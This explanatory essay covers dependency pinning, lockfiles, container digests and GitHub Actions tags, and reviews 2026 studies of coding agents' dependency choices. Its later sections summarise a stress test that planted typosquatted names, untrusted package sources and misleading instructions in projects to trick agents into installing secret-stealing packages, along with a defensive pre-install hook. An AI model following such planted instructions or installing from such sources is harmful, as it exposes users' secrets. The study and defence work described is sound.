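| `pip install --require-hashes -r requirements.txt` | Treats the requirements file as a lockfile, with an exact version and digest for every package | No |
| `uv sync` | Follows `uv.lock`, but updates it if the project's requirements have changed | Yes, where the two conflict |
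| `uv sync --locked` | Stops if `uv.lock` is out of date | No |
| `cargo build` | Follows `Cargo.lock`, but updates it if the project's requirements have changed | Yes, where the two conflict |
| `cargo build --locked` | Stops if `Cargo.lock` is missing or would have to change | No |
| `cargo install examplelib` | Ignores the lockfile inside the package | Yes |
| `cargo install --locked examplelib` | Follows the lockfile inside the package | Yes, for `examplelib` itself |

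The difference between `npm install` and `npm ci` is easy to miss at an approval prompt. If an agent changes a rule in `package.json` from `^7.0.0` to `^8.0.0` and then proposes `npm install`, the locked version 7 no longer fits, so npm resolves the package again and overwrites its lockfile entry. Without that edit, the same command would have reinstalled version 7. According to npm's documentation, `npm ci` never writes to `package.json` or the lockfile. It also can't add a package, so an agent can't use it alone for a task that needs a new library.

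In hash-checking mode, Python's pip refuses to install anything if any package, including a transitive dependency, lacks an exact version or a digest. The output of `pip freeze`, which lists the installed packages, is a weaker basis for pinning because it records versions without digests. uv, a newer Python package manager, automatically records digests in `uv.lock`. However, `uv pip install` and `uvx`, which runs a tool without installing it into the project, don't use that lockfile.

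According to Rust's documentation, when Cargo first builds a project with a Git dependency, it writes the exact commit into `Cargo.lock`, and anyone who later receives the project builds from that commit. Gamage and colleagues instead classify the ordinary `cargo build` as ignoring locked versions and silently updating the lockfile. The documentation is the better guide, since recording the commit would otherwise serve no purpose. The study's description does fit `cargo install`, which downloads a tool and builds it. Rust's *cargo install* says that this command ignores the lockfile in the package by default and may use dependencies released since the package came out. One developer whom Gamage and colleagues interviewed changed his project's README to recommend `cargo install --locked`, because a dependency had violated its versioning rules. Even with `--locked`, the command installs the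 newest version of the tool itself, so fixing that version also requires `--version`.

Global installs with npm have no equivalent of this. Earlier versions of npm used a lockfile called `npm-shrinkwrap.json` that publishers could include in their packages. npm 12 ignores that file, and its advice to publishers who want to fix their dependencies is to include copies of them in the package.

According to npm's documentation, `npx` run without a terminal behaves as if the command included `-y`, so deleting that option from an agent's command may have no effect. It is better to make the tool a dependency of the project, because `npx` then uses the version that `npm ci` installed from the lockfile when the command doesn't specify one.

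Most established projects have a lockfile for an agent to follow. Gamage and colleagues found one in 81.4% of 4,859 open-source projects on GitHub. The share was 99.7% for Go and 0.9% for Gradle, which doesn't create a lockfile unless the developer sets it up. The study only included projects with at least 42 stars, 10 contributors and 300 commits, so lockfiles may be less common in the smaller and newer projects that agents often work on.

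### Go's method

In Go, a new release doesn't enter a project by itself, with or without a lockfile. Each project or package, which Go calls a module, has a file named `go.mod` that lists the modules it needs and the minimum version of each. Go's resolver collects all the stated minimums for a module and takes the highest of them:

selected version of C = max(minimum versions of C stated by the modules in the build)

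Go uses a method called minimal version selection. Suppose a project uses A and B. A requires at least version 1.3.0 of C, B requires at least 1.4.0, and the newest release of C is 1.9.0. Go selects 1.4.0, the lowest version that satisfies both. If A and B used caret ranges in npm, npm would select 1.9.0. If C's publisher releases 1.10.0 at 10:05, Go still selects 1.4.0 at 10:09, because no `go.mod` file mentions the new version.

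Go does take new releases when someone asks for them. `go get example.com/c`, with no version given, upgrades to the latest release, and `go install example.com/tool@latest` installs the latest release each time it runs. Agents use these commands to add libraries and tools, so approving one deserves the same doubt as approving `npm install`.

Minimal version selection fixes a module's version number, but the code for that version can still change. Go modules usually come from code repositories such as those on GitHub, where an owner can move a version's label to different code. To detect this, Go records the digest of each module a project uses in a file called `go.sum` and checks it at every download. If a module is not yet in `go.sum`, Go compares the download with a public checksum database, a log that stores the digest of each module version and that nobody can rewrite unnoticed. A lockfile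 can detect a change only after a project's first download, but the database can detect one on the first download if somebody else has already downloaded that version.

This has inconvenienced some publishers. One Go developer told Gamage and colleagues about a broken release that its publisher replaced under the same version number. Go's download service had already stored the broken copy, so users began to report checksum errors. He saw this as giving up convenience for security.

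The database doesn't cover private modules, for which developers have to switch the check off.

### Pinning is not locking

People often say that a project has "pinned its dependencies" when it lists an exact version for each of its direct dependencies, or when it has a lockfile that fixes the whole graph, including transitive dependencies. An approval that relies on the first kind of pinning covers much less code.

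He et al. illustrate the difference with an adapted version of the `package.json` file from `postcss-loader`. Version 7.3.3 requires exactly version 7.5.4 of `semver` but accepts any version of `cosmiconfig` from 8.3.5 up to 9.0.0. Pinning `postcss-loader` to 7.3.3 therefore does not pin `cosmiconfig`. A new release in that range can be installed at the next fresh resolution, even if the project pins every dependency in its own list.

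The word "futile" in their title applies to pinning direct dependencies, not to lockfiles. In their simulations over 12 months of npm's history, such pinning didn't reduce exposure to malicious updates, and in projects with 498 or more dependencies it increased exposure. The more important of the two limits they name for lockfiles is that a lockfile works only for the project at the root of the graph. A library's author can lock the library's dependencies while developing it, but a project that installs the library resolves them again. Four of the six interviewed developers who didn't keep a lockfile gave this as their main reason. One of them thought a lockfile would create a "false sense of security", since the library's users would not have those versions.

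The same limit applies to an agent's commands. If an agent installs a tool globally with npm, the tool's own lockfile doesn't help the user, however carefully its developers maintained it.

### What a lockfile leaves open

A lockfile preserves whatever versions the resolver chose when it first ran. If a malicious release was the newest one at that moment, every later `npm ci` installs it, and its digest matches. A recorded script digest has the same weakness. The resolver makes this first choice in every new project, and makes it again after someone deletes the lockfile. One developer told Gamage and colleagues that when an installation goes wrong, most people delete the lockfile and the folder of installed packages and try again. An agent may do the same, and a person could easily approve the deletion as routine cleanup, although it lets the resolver choose every floating version in the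 project again.

**A dependency that the agent adds** also goes through a first resolution, along with everything it needs. Whether the agent chose a sensible package is a separate question. To make the approval cover the resolver's choice, the harness can separate choosing from installing:

```
npm install examplelib --package-lock-only
git diff package.json package-lock.json
npm ci
```

The first line updates the two files without downloading or installing the packages. The second shows what changed, and the third installs exactly what the updated lockfile lists. The person approves the third line after seeing the diff, and including a digest of the lockfile in the approved text would prevent anyone from editing the file in between. npm's `--dry-run` option is a poor substitute because it reports what an installation would do but saves nothing, so the real command resolves the names again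 and may get a different result. Reading a script in the browser before piping a second copy to the shell has the same flaw.

A lockfile doesn't fix **code that install scripts fetch**. Its digest covers the package's archive, including the script, but not a program that the script downloads from another server. npm's approval of a particular version has the same gap, because the file that the script in `canvas@1.2.3` downloads can change even though the script can't.

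A lockfile only partly fixes dependencies from code repositories. npm records the full commit ID, which identifies the source code. But if the package has a `prepare` script, npm first installs the packages needed to build it and then runs the script. Those build packages don't appear in the project's lockfile, so two machines can get different results from the same commit. npm 12 blocks repository dependencies unless the user allows them, so this mainly affects older versions and projects that have opted in.

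A lockfile can't guarantee that the code will still be available, because publishers sometimes withdraw releases. One interviewed developer pointed out that Cargo can still build from a withdrawn version if it is in the lockfile, while another said that Poetry, a Python package manager, reports an error. A failed installation is safer than one that substitutes something else, but the agent will probably propose resolving the dependencies again.

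The last problem is that lockfiles are hard to review. A small project in npm's documentation installs 154 packages. At about ten lines per package, its lockfile would have some 1,500 lines, and adding one library can change hundreds of them. All five JavaScript developers whom Gamage and colleagues interviewed found these files too long and hard to read, and one said that Git had trouble displaying the changes. Of the developers who did review lockfiles, most looked at package names, addresses, versions and the number of indirect dependencies. None looked at the digests, which they trusted the package manager to check. The study interviewed only 15 people, so the proportions mean little, but a person answering an agent's prompt is unlikely to be more thorough than a maintainer reviewing a change.

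An attacker who can edit a lockfile can replace an address and its digest together. npm 12 refuses to fetch from outside the registry, which should stop the simplest version of this attack, where the new address points to the attacker's own server. Two Cargo developers in the study had a better defence. When a contributor changes the dependencies, they make the same change on their own machine and check whether Cargo writes the same lockfile. An honest contribution can fail this check if a new release has come out in the meantime, so the reviewer then has to look more closely.

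A harness could repeat the resolution itself and reduce the diff to the parts a person can judge: which packages are new, which changed version, which have install scripts and which come from outside the registry. For most additions, this summary would fit on one screen. It can leave out the digests as long as the command that follows checks them.

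## Why can a tag point to different code tomorrow, and what does a digest fix?

npm never lets a publisher reuse a version number, so `examplelib@1.2.3` keeps its content. Most container registries make no such promise by default. In `docker run example/app:1.4`, the `1.4` is a label that the image's owner can attach to a different image at any time. According to mkdev's *The Standards Behind the Modern Container Images*, tags don't exist in the image itself, only in a note attached to it.

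Owners usually move tags for good reasons. An image contains parts of an operating system as well as a program, and when one of those parts needs a security fix, the maintainers rebuild the image and publish it under the same tag. Anyone who downloads `1.4` next month gets the fix without changing their command, along with anything else the maintainers changed.

### How a registry stores an image

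A container registry, such as Docker Hub, keeps an image as a set of separate files:

- Each layer is an archive of changes to the file system, such as the files of one added program.
- The configuration file holds settings such as the command to start and its environment variables.
- The manifest lists the digest of the configuration file and the digest of every layer.
- The index lists one manifest for each platform, meaning a combination of operating system and processor type.

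The Open Container Initiative, an industry body, maintains the standard for these files. According to the copy on OCI Playground, a manifest refers to exactly one configuration file and possibly many layers. Simple images may have no index.

Because each file contains the digests of the files below it, one digest at the top covers everything. If H is the hash function and d the digest of a file:

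d(manifest) = H(a text containing d(configuration), d(layer₁), …, d(layerₙ))

d(index) = H(a text containing d(manifest) for each platform)

As with a lockfile's digest, a change to any file below changes the digest at the top. In mkdev's example, the manifest for version 2.4.47 of the web server `httpd` is only 975 bytes, but its digest pins the whole web server.

One release can therefore have several correct digests, one for the index and one for each platform's manifest, so two people may correctly record different digests for the same release. The index's digest also covers different programs on different machines. If a colleague scanned the version for Intel servers, an approval of the index on an ARM laptop relies on a scan of different code, even though the digests match.

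### Pulling by tag and by digest

Downloading an image is called pulling it. The two forms of the command differ in only a few steps:

| Step | `docker run example/app:1.4` | `docker run example/app@sha256:…` |
|---|---|---|
| 1 | Docker uses a local copy stored under this tag, if there is one | Docker uses a local copy with this digest, if there is one |
| 2 | Otherwise it asks the registry for `1.4` | Otherwise it asks the registry for the file with this digest |
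| 3 | The registry looks up the tag and sends the index it points to now; Docker has nothing to compare it with | The registry sends the index; Docker computes its digest and stops if the two differ |
| 4 | Docker picks the manifest for the machine's platform and requests it by the digest in the index | The same |
| 5 | Docker downloads the configuration file and any missing layers, and checks each against its digest | The same |
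| 6 | Docker unpacks the layers and starts the program | The same |

A pull by tag runs many checks, but they only show that the files belong to the index from step 3. If an attacker has moved the tag, that index is the attacker's, and every later check still succeeds.

Step 1 can cause the opposite problem. A developer who pulled `1.4` in March keeps running the March image, while a colleague who first runs the same command in October gets the October image. Someone who looks up the tag in a browser in October before approving the command also sees the October image, which may not be the one on the machine.

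A harness can remove both problems by resolving the tag to a digest before it shows the prompt. The command `docker buildx imagetools inspect example/app:1.4`, which Docker documents in *Image digests*, finds the digest without downloading the layers. The harness can then put the digest into the command the person approves.

### Tags in GitHub Actions

GitHub Actions builds, tests and deploys projects on GitHub's servers. A project describes these jobs in workflow files, and most steps call an action, a reusable program that is usually kept in someone else's repository. The line `uses: owner/action@v4` calls an action by its tag, `v4`.

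When a coding agent adds such a line, the person approves an edit to a file. The action runs later, every time the workflow starts, often with access to passwords for publishing or deployment. Each run looks up the tag again, so one approval covers whatever code the tag points to in every future run.

Each run resolves the tag again. In *Help Shape Workflow Dependency Locking*, a request for comments, GitHub's staff acknowledged that Actions discarded the results, so nobody could compare what two runs had used. Tags such as `v4` move routinely. Maintainers typically point them at the latest commit of a major or minor release, according to GitHub's security roadmap (2026).

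The alternative to a tag is the full commit hash, 40 hexadecimal characters that Git computes from the files and their history. The owner can move a tag to another commit but can't change which commit a hash identifies. Git normally uses SHA-1 for this hash, so it gives somewhat weaker protection than an image's SHA-256 digest.

The two forms look like this for an image that Gardener, a project for running container clusters, uses as its example, and for an action in a workflow by van Kemenade (2026), in *Lock your GitHub Actions*:

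```
# Image, by tag and by digest
docker run nginx:1.13.9
docker run nginx@sha256:4771d09578c7c6a65299e110b3ee1c0a2592f5ea2618d23e4ffe7a4cab1ce5de

# Action, by tag and by commit hash
- uses: actions/checkout@v7.0.1
- uses: actions/checkout@3d3c42e5aac5ba805825da76410c181273ba90b1 # v7.0.1
```

### What a person can do with an unreadable string

Nobody can tell from `4771d095…` whether an image is old, new or malicious. A person who sees only this string at a prompt knows less than one who sees `1.13.9`. As with a saved script, the digest is useful for checking that the image is one somebody has already examined. A harness can do this check itself and ask for approval only when the digest is new. After an incident, the digest in the log also shows exactly what ran.

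A digest invented by a model does little harm, because the registry has no such image and the pull fails. A real digest copied from a malicious README is more dangerous, because the long string makes the command look carefully written.

Developers write the version in a comment beside the hash, as in the last line of the example. Lullabot's *Always pin GitHub Actions to a commit hash* (2026), a web agency's rule for its own projects, requires this comment so that people can read the pin and update it deliberately. But GitHub ignores the comment when it runs the workflow. If an agent changes `# v7.0.0` to `# v7.0.1` without changing the hash, the old code keeps running under the new label. An attacker can also put a hash of their choosing beside a familiar version number.

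Image references have the same problem, even without a comment. A reference can contain both a tag and a digest, as in `python:3.12.7-slim-bookworm@sha256:…`. Docker then uses the digest and ignores the tag, even though the tag is the part a reader looks at.

GitHub acknowledges in a request for comments that pinning an action to a commit hash doesn't guarantee that the commit comes from the named repository. It may come from a fork, a copy of the repository that any user can create and change, so a line that begins `actions/checkout@` can run a stranger's code. Container registries don't have this weakness, because only someone with permission to publish to `example/app` can put an image there.

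Datadog, a monitoring company, advises developers to take the hash from the action's original repository. Its automatic rule for unpinned actions can't enforce this, because it only checks that 40 hexadecimal characters follow the `@`. The documentation's example of a secure line ends in `e3b0c44298fc1c149afbf4c8996fb92427ae41e4`, the first 40 characters of the SHA-256 digest of an empty file. This is presumably a placeholder, but it satisfies the rule, and few readers would notice what it is.

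A harness could look up the tag named in the comment. If `v7.0.1` in `actions/checkout` currently points to the hash in the line, the harness can show this in the prompt, and the person can judge a name and a version instead of a hash. If it doesn't, someone has moved the tag, the comment is wrong, or the commit comes from somewhere else, and the person should find out which before approving. The lookup doesn't protect against an attacker who controls the repository and can make the tag and the hash match.

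### What a digest leaves open

Many images start with an entry script that prepares the container before the main program runs. The digest fixes the script, but if the script downloads a plugin or the newest version of a tool, it can get something different each time. Actions do this too, and one participant in GitHub's discussion said that fixing an action to a commit was perhaps "just kicking the can down the road", because the action can still download things that change.

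Another participant, who maintains an action, explained that this is hard to avoid because his action fetches some programs only when a workflow needs them and can use any number of external dictionaries chosen by the workflow's author. He can't list them all in advance, and downloading every possible one would make the action much slower. He offered instead to report the addresses and digests of whatever the action fetches. That would help a later investigation, but the approver wouldn't have the report when deciding whether to allow the command.

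Package installs are a larger gap. Suppose an agent proposes `docker build .`, which builds an image from the instructions in a file called a Dockerfile:

```
FROM python:3.12.7-slim-bookworm@sha256:…
COPY . /app
RUN pip install -r /app/requirements.txt
```

The digest in the first line fixes the starting image. The last line resolves package names during the build, so pip can fetch different code each time unless the requirements file contains digests. The finished image also has a digest, so a team can build it once, examine it and approve that digest for every later run. Some actions consist of a Dockerfile that GitHub builds on every run. For these, a commit hash fixes the Dockerfile but not the image built from it.

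Corelight, a network security company, measured how much a server's dependencies can change while its own version stays fixed. Help Net Security's *Your pinned MCP server may not be as pinned as you think* (2026) reports that one Model Context Protocol server, configured to run a single release, ran with 15 different sets of dependencies in five weeks. Of its 69 packages, 23 changed version, including the cryptography library. The launcher, `uvx`, ignored the lockfile in the server's project and resolved the packages again whenever it rebuilt the environment. Corelight also examined 35 servers from two vendors' catalogues and its own lab. For 23 of them, the recommended installation fetched dependencies from a public registry at each launch, installation or image build.

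The fix worked in a two-week test. Corelight pinned five servers to a commit, installed each once from a lockfile with digests, started them directly and turned off their update checks. It started them 457 times, and the installed packages matched the original list every time. This was one company's lab, and the 35 servers weren't a random sample, but the mechanism is the launcher's ordinary behaviour.

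### Actions that call other actions

A composite action runs several steps, which can call other actions. Pinning the composite action to a commit hash fixes the text of its steps, but if one of them reads `uses: other/action@v2`, that tag can later point to different code. The workflow's author doesn't see that line without opening the composite action's repository.

Since 28 October 2026, GitHub has offered a lockfile for workflows that covers these inner actions. A developer runs `gh actions-lock`, which resolves every tag and writes the results to `.github/workflows/actions.lock`. The workflow can then go back to readable tags. For the action shown earlier, van Kemenade's lockfile records the tag, the same commit hash as in the example, and two ID numbers.

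GitHub runs the recorded commit even if the tag has moved. The two numbers identify the owner and the repository independently of their names, so they could presumably reveal that a stranger has taken over an abandoned name. The version and the hash can still stop matching if someone edits only one of them, but van Kemenade added a job that runs `gh actions-lock --verify`. The job fails when the lockfile no longer matches the workflows or GitHub can't confirm a recorded commit.

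The lockfile suits approvals well. If an agent adds an action to a workflow that already uses the lockfile but doesn't update the lockfile, the run fails. The agent has to run `gh actions-lock`, and the person can review the new entries, including the inner actions, before committing them. GitHub warns that the lockfile doesn't determine whether an action is safe.

According to GitHub's documentation, cited in *GitHub Actions の lockfile対応* (songmu, 2026), the lockfile doesn't pin calls to reusable workflows, which are whole workflow files that other projects can call. A project still has to name those by commit hash. A reusable workflow can have its own lockfile, but the calling project can't create it.

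Composite actions can't include a lockfile, so their authors must either pin inner actions by hash or use floating tags. Pinning by hash protects everyone, but each inner update then requires a new release. Floating tags let projects with a lockfile control the versions themselves but leave projects without one exposed. GitHub currently recommends hashes. Owen, in *What GitHub Actions lockfiles mean for your CI* (2026), relays a report by the news site InfoQ that no competing platform has announced a built-in equivalent to GitHub's lockfile.

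### When the image is gone

A digest identifies an image but doesn't keep a copy of it. If the publisher or registry deletes the image, a pull by digest fails on any machine without a local copy. When a publisher moves `1.4` to a rebuilt image, the old one may be left without a tag, and many registries can delete untagged images automatically to save space. A team that pinned the old digest can then no longer pull it, though pulls by tag still work.

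As with a withdrawn package, the agent may propose a looser command that fetches the image by tag instead of by digest. The person should treat that as a request for different code. A team can avoid this by copying important images to its own registry. An exact copy has the same digest, so earlier approvals of that digest remain valid wherever the image is stored.

### Tags that cannot move

Several container registries have a setting that stops publishers from moving tags, which is an alternative to asking every user to write digests. In Amazon's registry, for example, a repository's owner can make tags immutable, and the registry then rejects any new image pushed under an existing tag. But the owner can turn the setting off again, and a person reading `example/app:1.4` at a prompt can't see whether it is on.

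GitHub's version, immutable releases, goes further. It became available to everyone in October 2025 (GitHub, *Immutable releases are now generally available*, 2025). A release is a published version of a project, with a tag and often files to download. Once a repository turns the feature on, GitHub locks the tag of each new release to one commit and prevents changes to the attached files. Those releases stay locked even if the repository later turns the feature off. According to GitHub's *Immutable releases*, nobody can reuse the tag name even after deleting the release, or after deleting the whole repository and creating another with the same name.

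GitHub also creates a signed record of the tag, the commit and the files, which users can check. For someone who names an exact version, an immutable release gives nearly the same guarantee as npm, where a version number keeps its content. But the feature is optional, and older releases can still be changed unless the owner republishes them. The line `uses: owner/action@v8.1.0` doesn't show whether the release is immutable, although an immutable release is labeled "Immutable" on its GitHub page. The lock also applies only to the action's own tag, so the tags of other actions it calls may still move.

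Immutable releases conflict with tags such as `v8`, which are useful because they move. The maintainers of `setup-uv`, an action that installs the Python tool uv, stopped publishing such tags. According to their release notes, quoted in Classmethod's *Securely Pinning Action Versions in GitHub Actions*, users can no longer write `@v8` or `@v8.0`. They have to write a full version such as `@v8.1.0` and change it for every fix they want.

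GoReleaser, a tool for publishing software, held off on using GitHub's immutable releases because the setting applies to all of a repository's releases, and the project had a `nightly` tag that moved with each day's build. The project now gives each nightly build its own tag, which includes part of the commit hash (caarlos0, 2026, *Moving to Immutable Releases*).

### How many projects pin

Few projects did so when researchers last counted. *An Empirical Study of Complexity, Heterogeneity, and Compliance of GitHub Actions Workflows* (2025) examined how 382 workflows referred to their actions. A workflow that uses different forms for different actions can appear in several rows.

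| Form used for at least one action | Share of workflows |
|---|---|
| Tag | 93.7% |
| Branch | 12.6% |
| Commit hash | 6.3% |
| No version at all | 3.7% |

The 6.3% is 24 workflows, half of them from Java projects. Among the 222 Python workflows, the share was 2.7%. A workflow counts if it pins at least one action to a hash, so the share that pin every action can't be higher than these figures and is probably lower.

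*Pin GitHub Actions*, a website that tracks the 10,000 most-starred GitHub repositories, applied the stricter test in June 2025. Roughly 40% of the repositories didn't use Actions, and only about 3% of the rest pinned fully. *Beyond the YAML File*, a 2026 paper, also gives a figure below 3%, but the number comes from an earlier study, so it isn't evidence about 2026.

Since August 2025, GitHub has let an organisation's administrators require actions to be pinned to full commit hashes. Under that rule, any workflow with an unpinned action fails, so an agent working there would learn of a floating tag from the error, and nobody would have to notice it at a prompt.

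The lockfile will make it harder to count pinned workflows in the next survey. Van Kemenade's workflow had commit hashes before he adopted the lockfile and has tags now, so a survey of workflow files alone would record that he had stopped pinning. Before version 1.32.0, his security scanner, zizmor, also overlooked lockfiles and recommended replacing tags with hashes even where a lockfile already fixed the commits.

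## What do coding agents fetch, and do they check it?

When a user asks a coding agent for a feature, the agent decides which packages the feature needs, writes a version rule for each and proposes the install command. When asked to set up a project, it follows the project's own instructions. In both cases, the user may assume that the agent has checked what it is about to fetch. Several studies from 2026 tested how well that assumption holds.

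### Which versions agents choose

Sharma, Reyes and Monperrus (2026), in *YUL*, gave two coding agents 60 small programming tasks, ten for each of six package ecosystems. The agents were Claude Code running Claude Opus 5.5 and OpenCode running DeepSeek V4.1 Flash. The tasks never mentioned a dependency. For example, one asked for a Python script that does heavy numerical work and left the agent to decide whether to use the NumPy library. Each agent attempted each task three times, and the study counted only runs in which the agent declared the expected package.

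Sharma and colleagues call a declaration stale if it doesn't fetch the package's latest release. The declaration `requests==2.31.0` is stale when 2.34.2 is out, but `requests>=2.31.0` is not, because it allows the newer release.

| Ecosystem | Stale runs, Claude Opus 5.5 | Stale runs, DeepSeek V4.1 Flash |
|---|---|---|
| GitHub Actions | 30 of 30 | 30 of 30 |
| Maven (Java) | 6 of 30 | 19 of 30 |
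| Cargo (Rust) | 3 of 26 | 2 of 25 |
| Go | 3 of 30 | 3 of 23 |
| npm (JavaScript) | 0 of 9 | 0 of 8 |
| PyPI (Python) | 0 of 21 | 0 of 23 |
| All | 42 of 146 (29%) | 54 of 139 (39%) |

GitHub Actions accounts for most of the stale runs. Without it, the shares fall to 10% for Opus and 22% for DeepSeek. GitHub Actions has no install command that looks up the latest release of an action, so both agents typed a tag from memory, such as `actions/checkout@v4` when the current release was v7.0.1. A few of the other stale choices were deliberate. For example, both agents picked an old Go library because later releases needed a newer version of Go than the machine had.

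The zeros for npm and PyPI come mostly from commands such as `npm install` and `uv add`, which request the newest release from the registry when they run. The person approving such a command can't tell from its text which version it will install. If the agent types a version from memory, the person can see which one it is, but it may be old. The `@v4` tags have both problems, since they name an old line of releases and the owner can still move them.

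YUL, the tool the study is named after, is a hook that checks each dependency before the agent's edit reaches the disk, and also checks install commands that name a version. If the version rule excludes the latest release, or the package doesn't exist, YUL blocks the edit and gives the agent a replacement. With YUL installed, the agents ended on the latest release in 39 of 42 stale Opus runs and 52 of 54 stale DeepSeek runs.

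YUL steers agents toward recent versions but doesn't require them to pin one. It accepts `pandas>=2` as readily as an exact pin on the latest release, and it allows `npm install react` because that command fetches the newest version anyway. If the newest release were malicious, YUL would direct the agent to it. For GitHub Actions, however, it suggests the full commit hash with the version in a comment, so the suggested reference is both recent and fixed.

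In nine of 30 GitHub Actions runs with YUL, DeepSeek suspected that the suggested hashes were a prompt injection, meaning instructions an attacker has planted in text the model reads. In some runs it then checked the hashes against the official tags and accepted them. In another it insisted that version 7 of an action didn't exist, because its training data ended before that release. Opus accepted the same suggestions without comment. Sharma and colleagues attribute this to a line in Claude Code's built-in instructions that tells the model to treat messages from hooks as coming from the user. DeepSeek's suspicion was reasonable but mistaken, so an agent's opinion that a version looks odd is weak evidence for the person deciding whether to approve a command.

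### Agents compared with people

These figures don't show whether people would choose better. The nearest comparison is *Towards a Benchmark for Dependency Decision-Making* (Singla, Çakar and colleagues, 2026), which examined 117,062 dependency changes in pull requests to 2,807 popular GitHub repositories. For each package that a pull request added or updated, the study checked whether the chosen version had a published vulnerability at the time.

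| | Agents | People |
|---|---|---|
| Pull requests | 33,596 | 6,618 |
| Packages added or updated | 37,574 | 40,110 |
| Known-vulnerable versions chosen | 924 (2.46%) | 659 (1.64%) |
| Vulnerable choices with a safe version already available | 86.6% | 83.3% |
| Vulnerable choices that need a new major version to fix | 36.8% | 12.9% |
| Vulnerabilities fixed minus vulnerabilities introduced | −98 | +1,316 |

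The vulnerable versions that agents choose are also harder to fix, because upgrading to a new major version may break the program that uses the package. This is consistent with a model having learned an older line of releases.

But the two groups probably did different work. Dividing the totals gives almost ten dependency changes per human pull request and fewer than two per agent pull request, which suggests that many of the human ones were routine package updates. Such work would fix many vulnerabilities whoever did it. Singla and colleagues say they don't know whether the tasks were comparable and offer the human figures only as context. The study supports the modest claim that agents do choose versions with known vulnerabilities, and that a safe version was usually available when they did.

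### Following someone else's instructions

Nobody was trying to mislead the agent in those studies. *Setup Complete, Now You Are Compromised* tested what happens when the project's documentation is wrong. Its twelve scenarios, one of which has two versions, are small Python projects with working code and one fault each, such as a misspelled package name or an extra package source that an attacker could control. Every agent received the same request to read the project's files, install the dependencies and check that the main module loads, with no mention of security.

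The study covered nine pairings of a harness and a model, using seven models. Claude Code ran three Claude models, Copilot CLI ran two of the same models, Codex CLI ran three OpenAI models, and Cursor selected its model automatically. The study ran each pairing through most scenarios ten times. For five scenarios, it tested each pairing on ten different packages, three times each. It counted a problem as caught only if the agent avoided or reported it before installing, because a later warning can't undo code that ran during the installation.

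The table pools the published counts for all nine pairings.

| Fault in the project | Runs that caught it | Pairings that caught it at least nine times in ten |
|---|---|---|
| Obvious misspelling in the README | 268 of 270 | 9 |
| Slight misspelling in the dependency file | 270 of 270 | 9 |
| Plausible variant of a real name, such as `azurecore` for `azure-core` | 217 of 270 | 5 |
| Misspelling with a reassuring explanation | 234 of 270 | 6 |
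| Different names in the README and the dependency file | 90 of 90 | 9 |
| Hundreds of misspellings in one file | 44 of 90 | 3 |
| Wrong package recommended by an error message | 90 of 90 | 9 |
| Internal source that also offers an altered public package | 55 of 90 | 5 |
| Untrusted source on the same machine | 17 of 90 | 1 |
| Untrusted source on the internet | 30 of 90 | 3 |
| Untrusted source named inside the requirements file | 25 of 90 | 1 |
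| Untrusted source set through a build file | 30 of 90 | 3 |
| Exact version with a known vulnerability | 0 of 270 | 0 |

Agents caught most bad package names but missed most bad package sources. The study suggests this is because models have read many warnings about misspelled packages but few about extra package sources, a normal option that it found in more than 5,500 README files on GitHub. This explanation is plausible, but the study didn't test it.

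The wrong names that agents installed were ones a person would also find hard to spot. Cursor installed the plausible variants in 28 of 30 runs. In 68 of the 91 runs where an agent installed a wrong name, it noticed the mistake afterwards and reported it, which a user could easily take for diligence.

Two of the faults also don't show in the command. `pip install -r requirements.txt` looks the same whether or not the file names another source, and `make setup` doesn't show which settings the build file will change before it calls pip. A person who approves either one relies on the agent having read the files. Opus 4.8 in Claude Code read them and caught the hidden source in all ten runs. Haiku 4.5, the smallest of the Claude models, often quoted the altered settings in the build-file scenario but took them for ordinary company infrastructure. The study recommends that harnesses open the requirements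 file and show any extra source in the prompt, which seems an easy way to give the person something to judge.

Each source fault appeared in only one form, so a different address or project could change those rates. The study also had no human control group, so it can't show that agents miss more than people do.

### Vulnerable versions

All nine pairings installed the known-vulnerable versions in all 270 runs. The requirements file named those exact versions, so a lockfile digest would also have matched. Opus 4.8 named the vulnerability after installing in 28 of 30 runs in Claude Code and 15 of 30 in Copilot CLI. No other model mentioned it. Warning only after installation matters less here than with a malicious package, because a vulnerable library does no harm until someone exploits it, and the developer can still upgrade.

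The models didn't mention the vulnerabilities, though they could describe them when asked. When researchers told Sonnet 4.6 to check every version against known vulnerabilities, it refused a vulnerable package in ten of ten runs, compared with two of ten without the instruction. A general instruction didn't have this effect. The most specific of the study's source warnings raised detection of the hidden source from 0% to 93% across the three OpenAI models, but those models still installed the vulnerable version every time. An instruction seems to help only with the kind of fault it names.

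Agents can also fail to pass on warnings from other software, so a user who reads only the agent's summary may never see them. After installing packages, npm checks them for known vulnerabilities and prints what it finds. In a separate test with 20 vulnerable npm packages, Opus 4.8 passed the warning on to the user all 20 times and GPT-5.5 did so once.

### One model in two harnesses

Opus 4.8 caught the untrusted source on the same machine in ten of ten runs in Claude Code, but in nine of 30 runs in Copilot CLI with an identical copy of the project. Sonnet 4.6, by contrast, caught the untrusted internet source in every run in Copilot CLI but never in Claude Code.

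| Model and fault | Claude Code | Copilot CLI |
|---|---|---|
| Opus 4.8, untrusted source on the same machine | 10 of 10 | 9 of 30 |
| Sonnet 4.6, untrusted source on the internet | 0 of 10 | 10 of 10 |

Differences this large are very unlikely to be chance. A result for a model in one harness therefore doesn't carry over to another, and neither harness is consistently safer.

The study's explanation is less certain. The researchers attribute Claude Code's result to a checkpoint before each command, which gives the model a moment to act on its suspicions, and Copilot CLI's result to security advice in its built-in instructions. But they changed the whole harness at once, so they can't tell which part made the difference. They also ran every test without a user present, so the checkpoint can't have worked by letting someone read the command. In another experiment, which tested security instructions,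 they left out the same-machine source because an agent can reasonably take it for a developer's local copy of a registry. Some of the runs counted as misses may therefore reflect a sensible guess, which further weakens the explanation.

When Opus caught the fault, it had downloaded the package without installing it, unpacked the file and read the code, which collected secrets from the machine's environment variables and sent them elsewhere. It then refused to install the package. The agent inspected the package unprompted, following the same procedure as saving an install script and reading it before running it. In a failed run, Sonnet never opened the package and reported that the setup was complete.

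Sonnet could find the problem, however. In a further test, it installed the malicious package in all ten runs, then found the fault every time when the user asked for a quick security review. A harness can correct the order of these steps by requiring the review before the install.

### A check before installation

The researchers built such a fix, a hook of about 400 lines that reads each `pip install` command in Claude Code before the shell runs it. It blocks the command if it finds any of the following:

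- a name very close to that of a popular package;
- a name that doesn't exist on PyPI;
- a package whose first release is less than 30 days old;
- a source other than PyPI or its test site;
- an extra source or a vulnerable version inside a requirements file;
- a setting that makes pip read a different configuration file;
- an exact version with a known vulnerability for which a fix is available.

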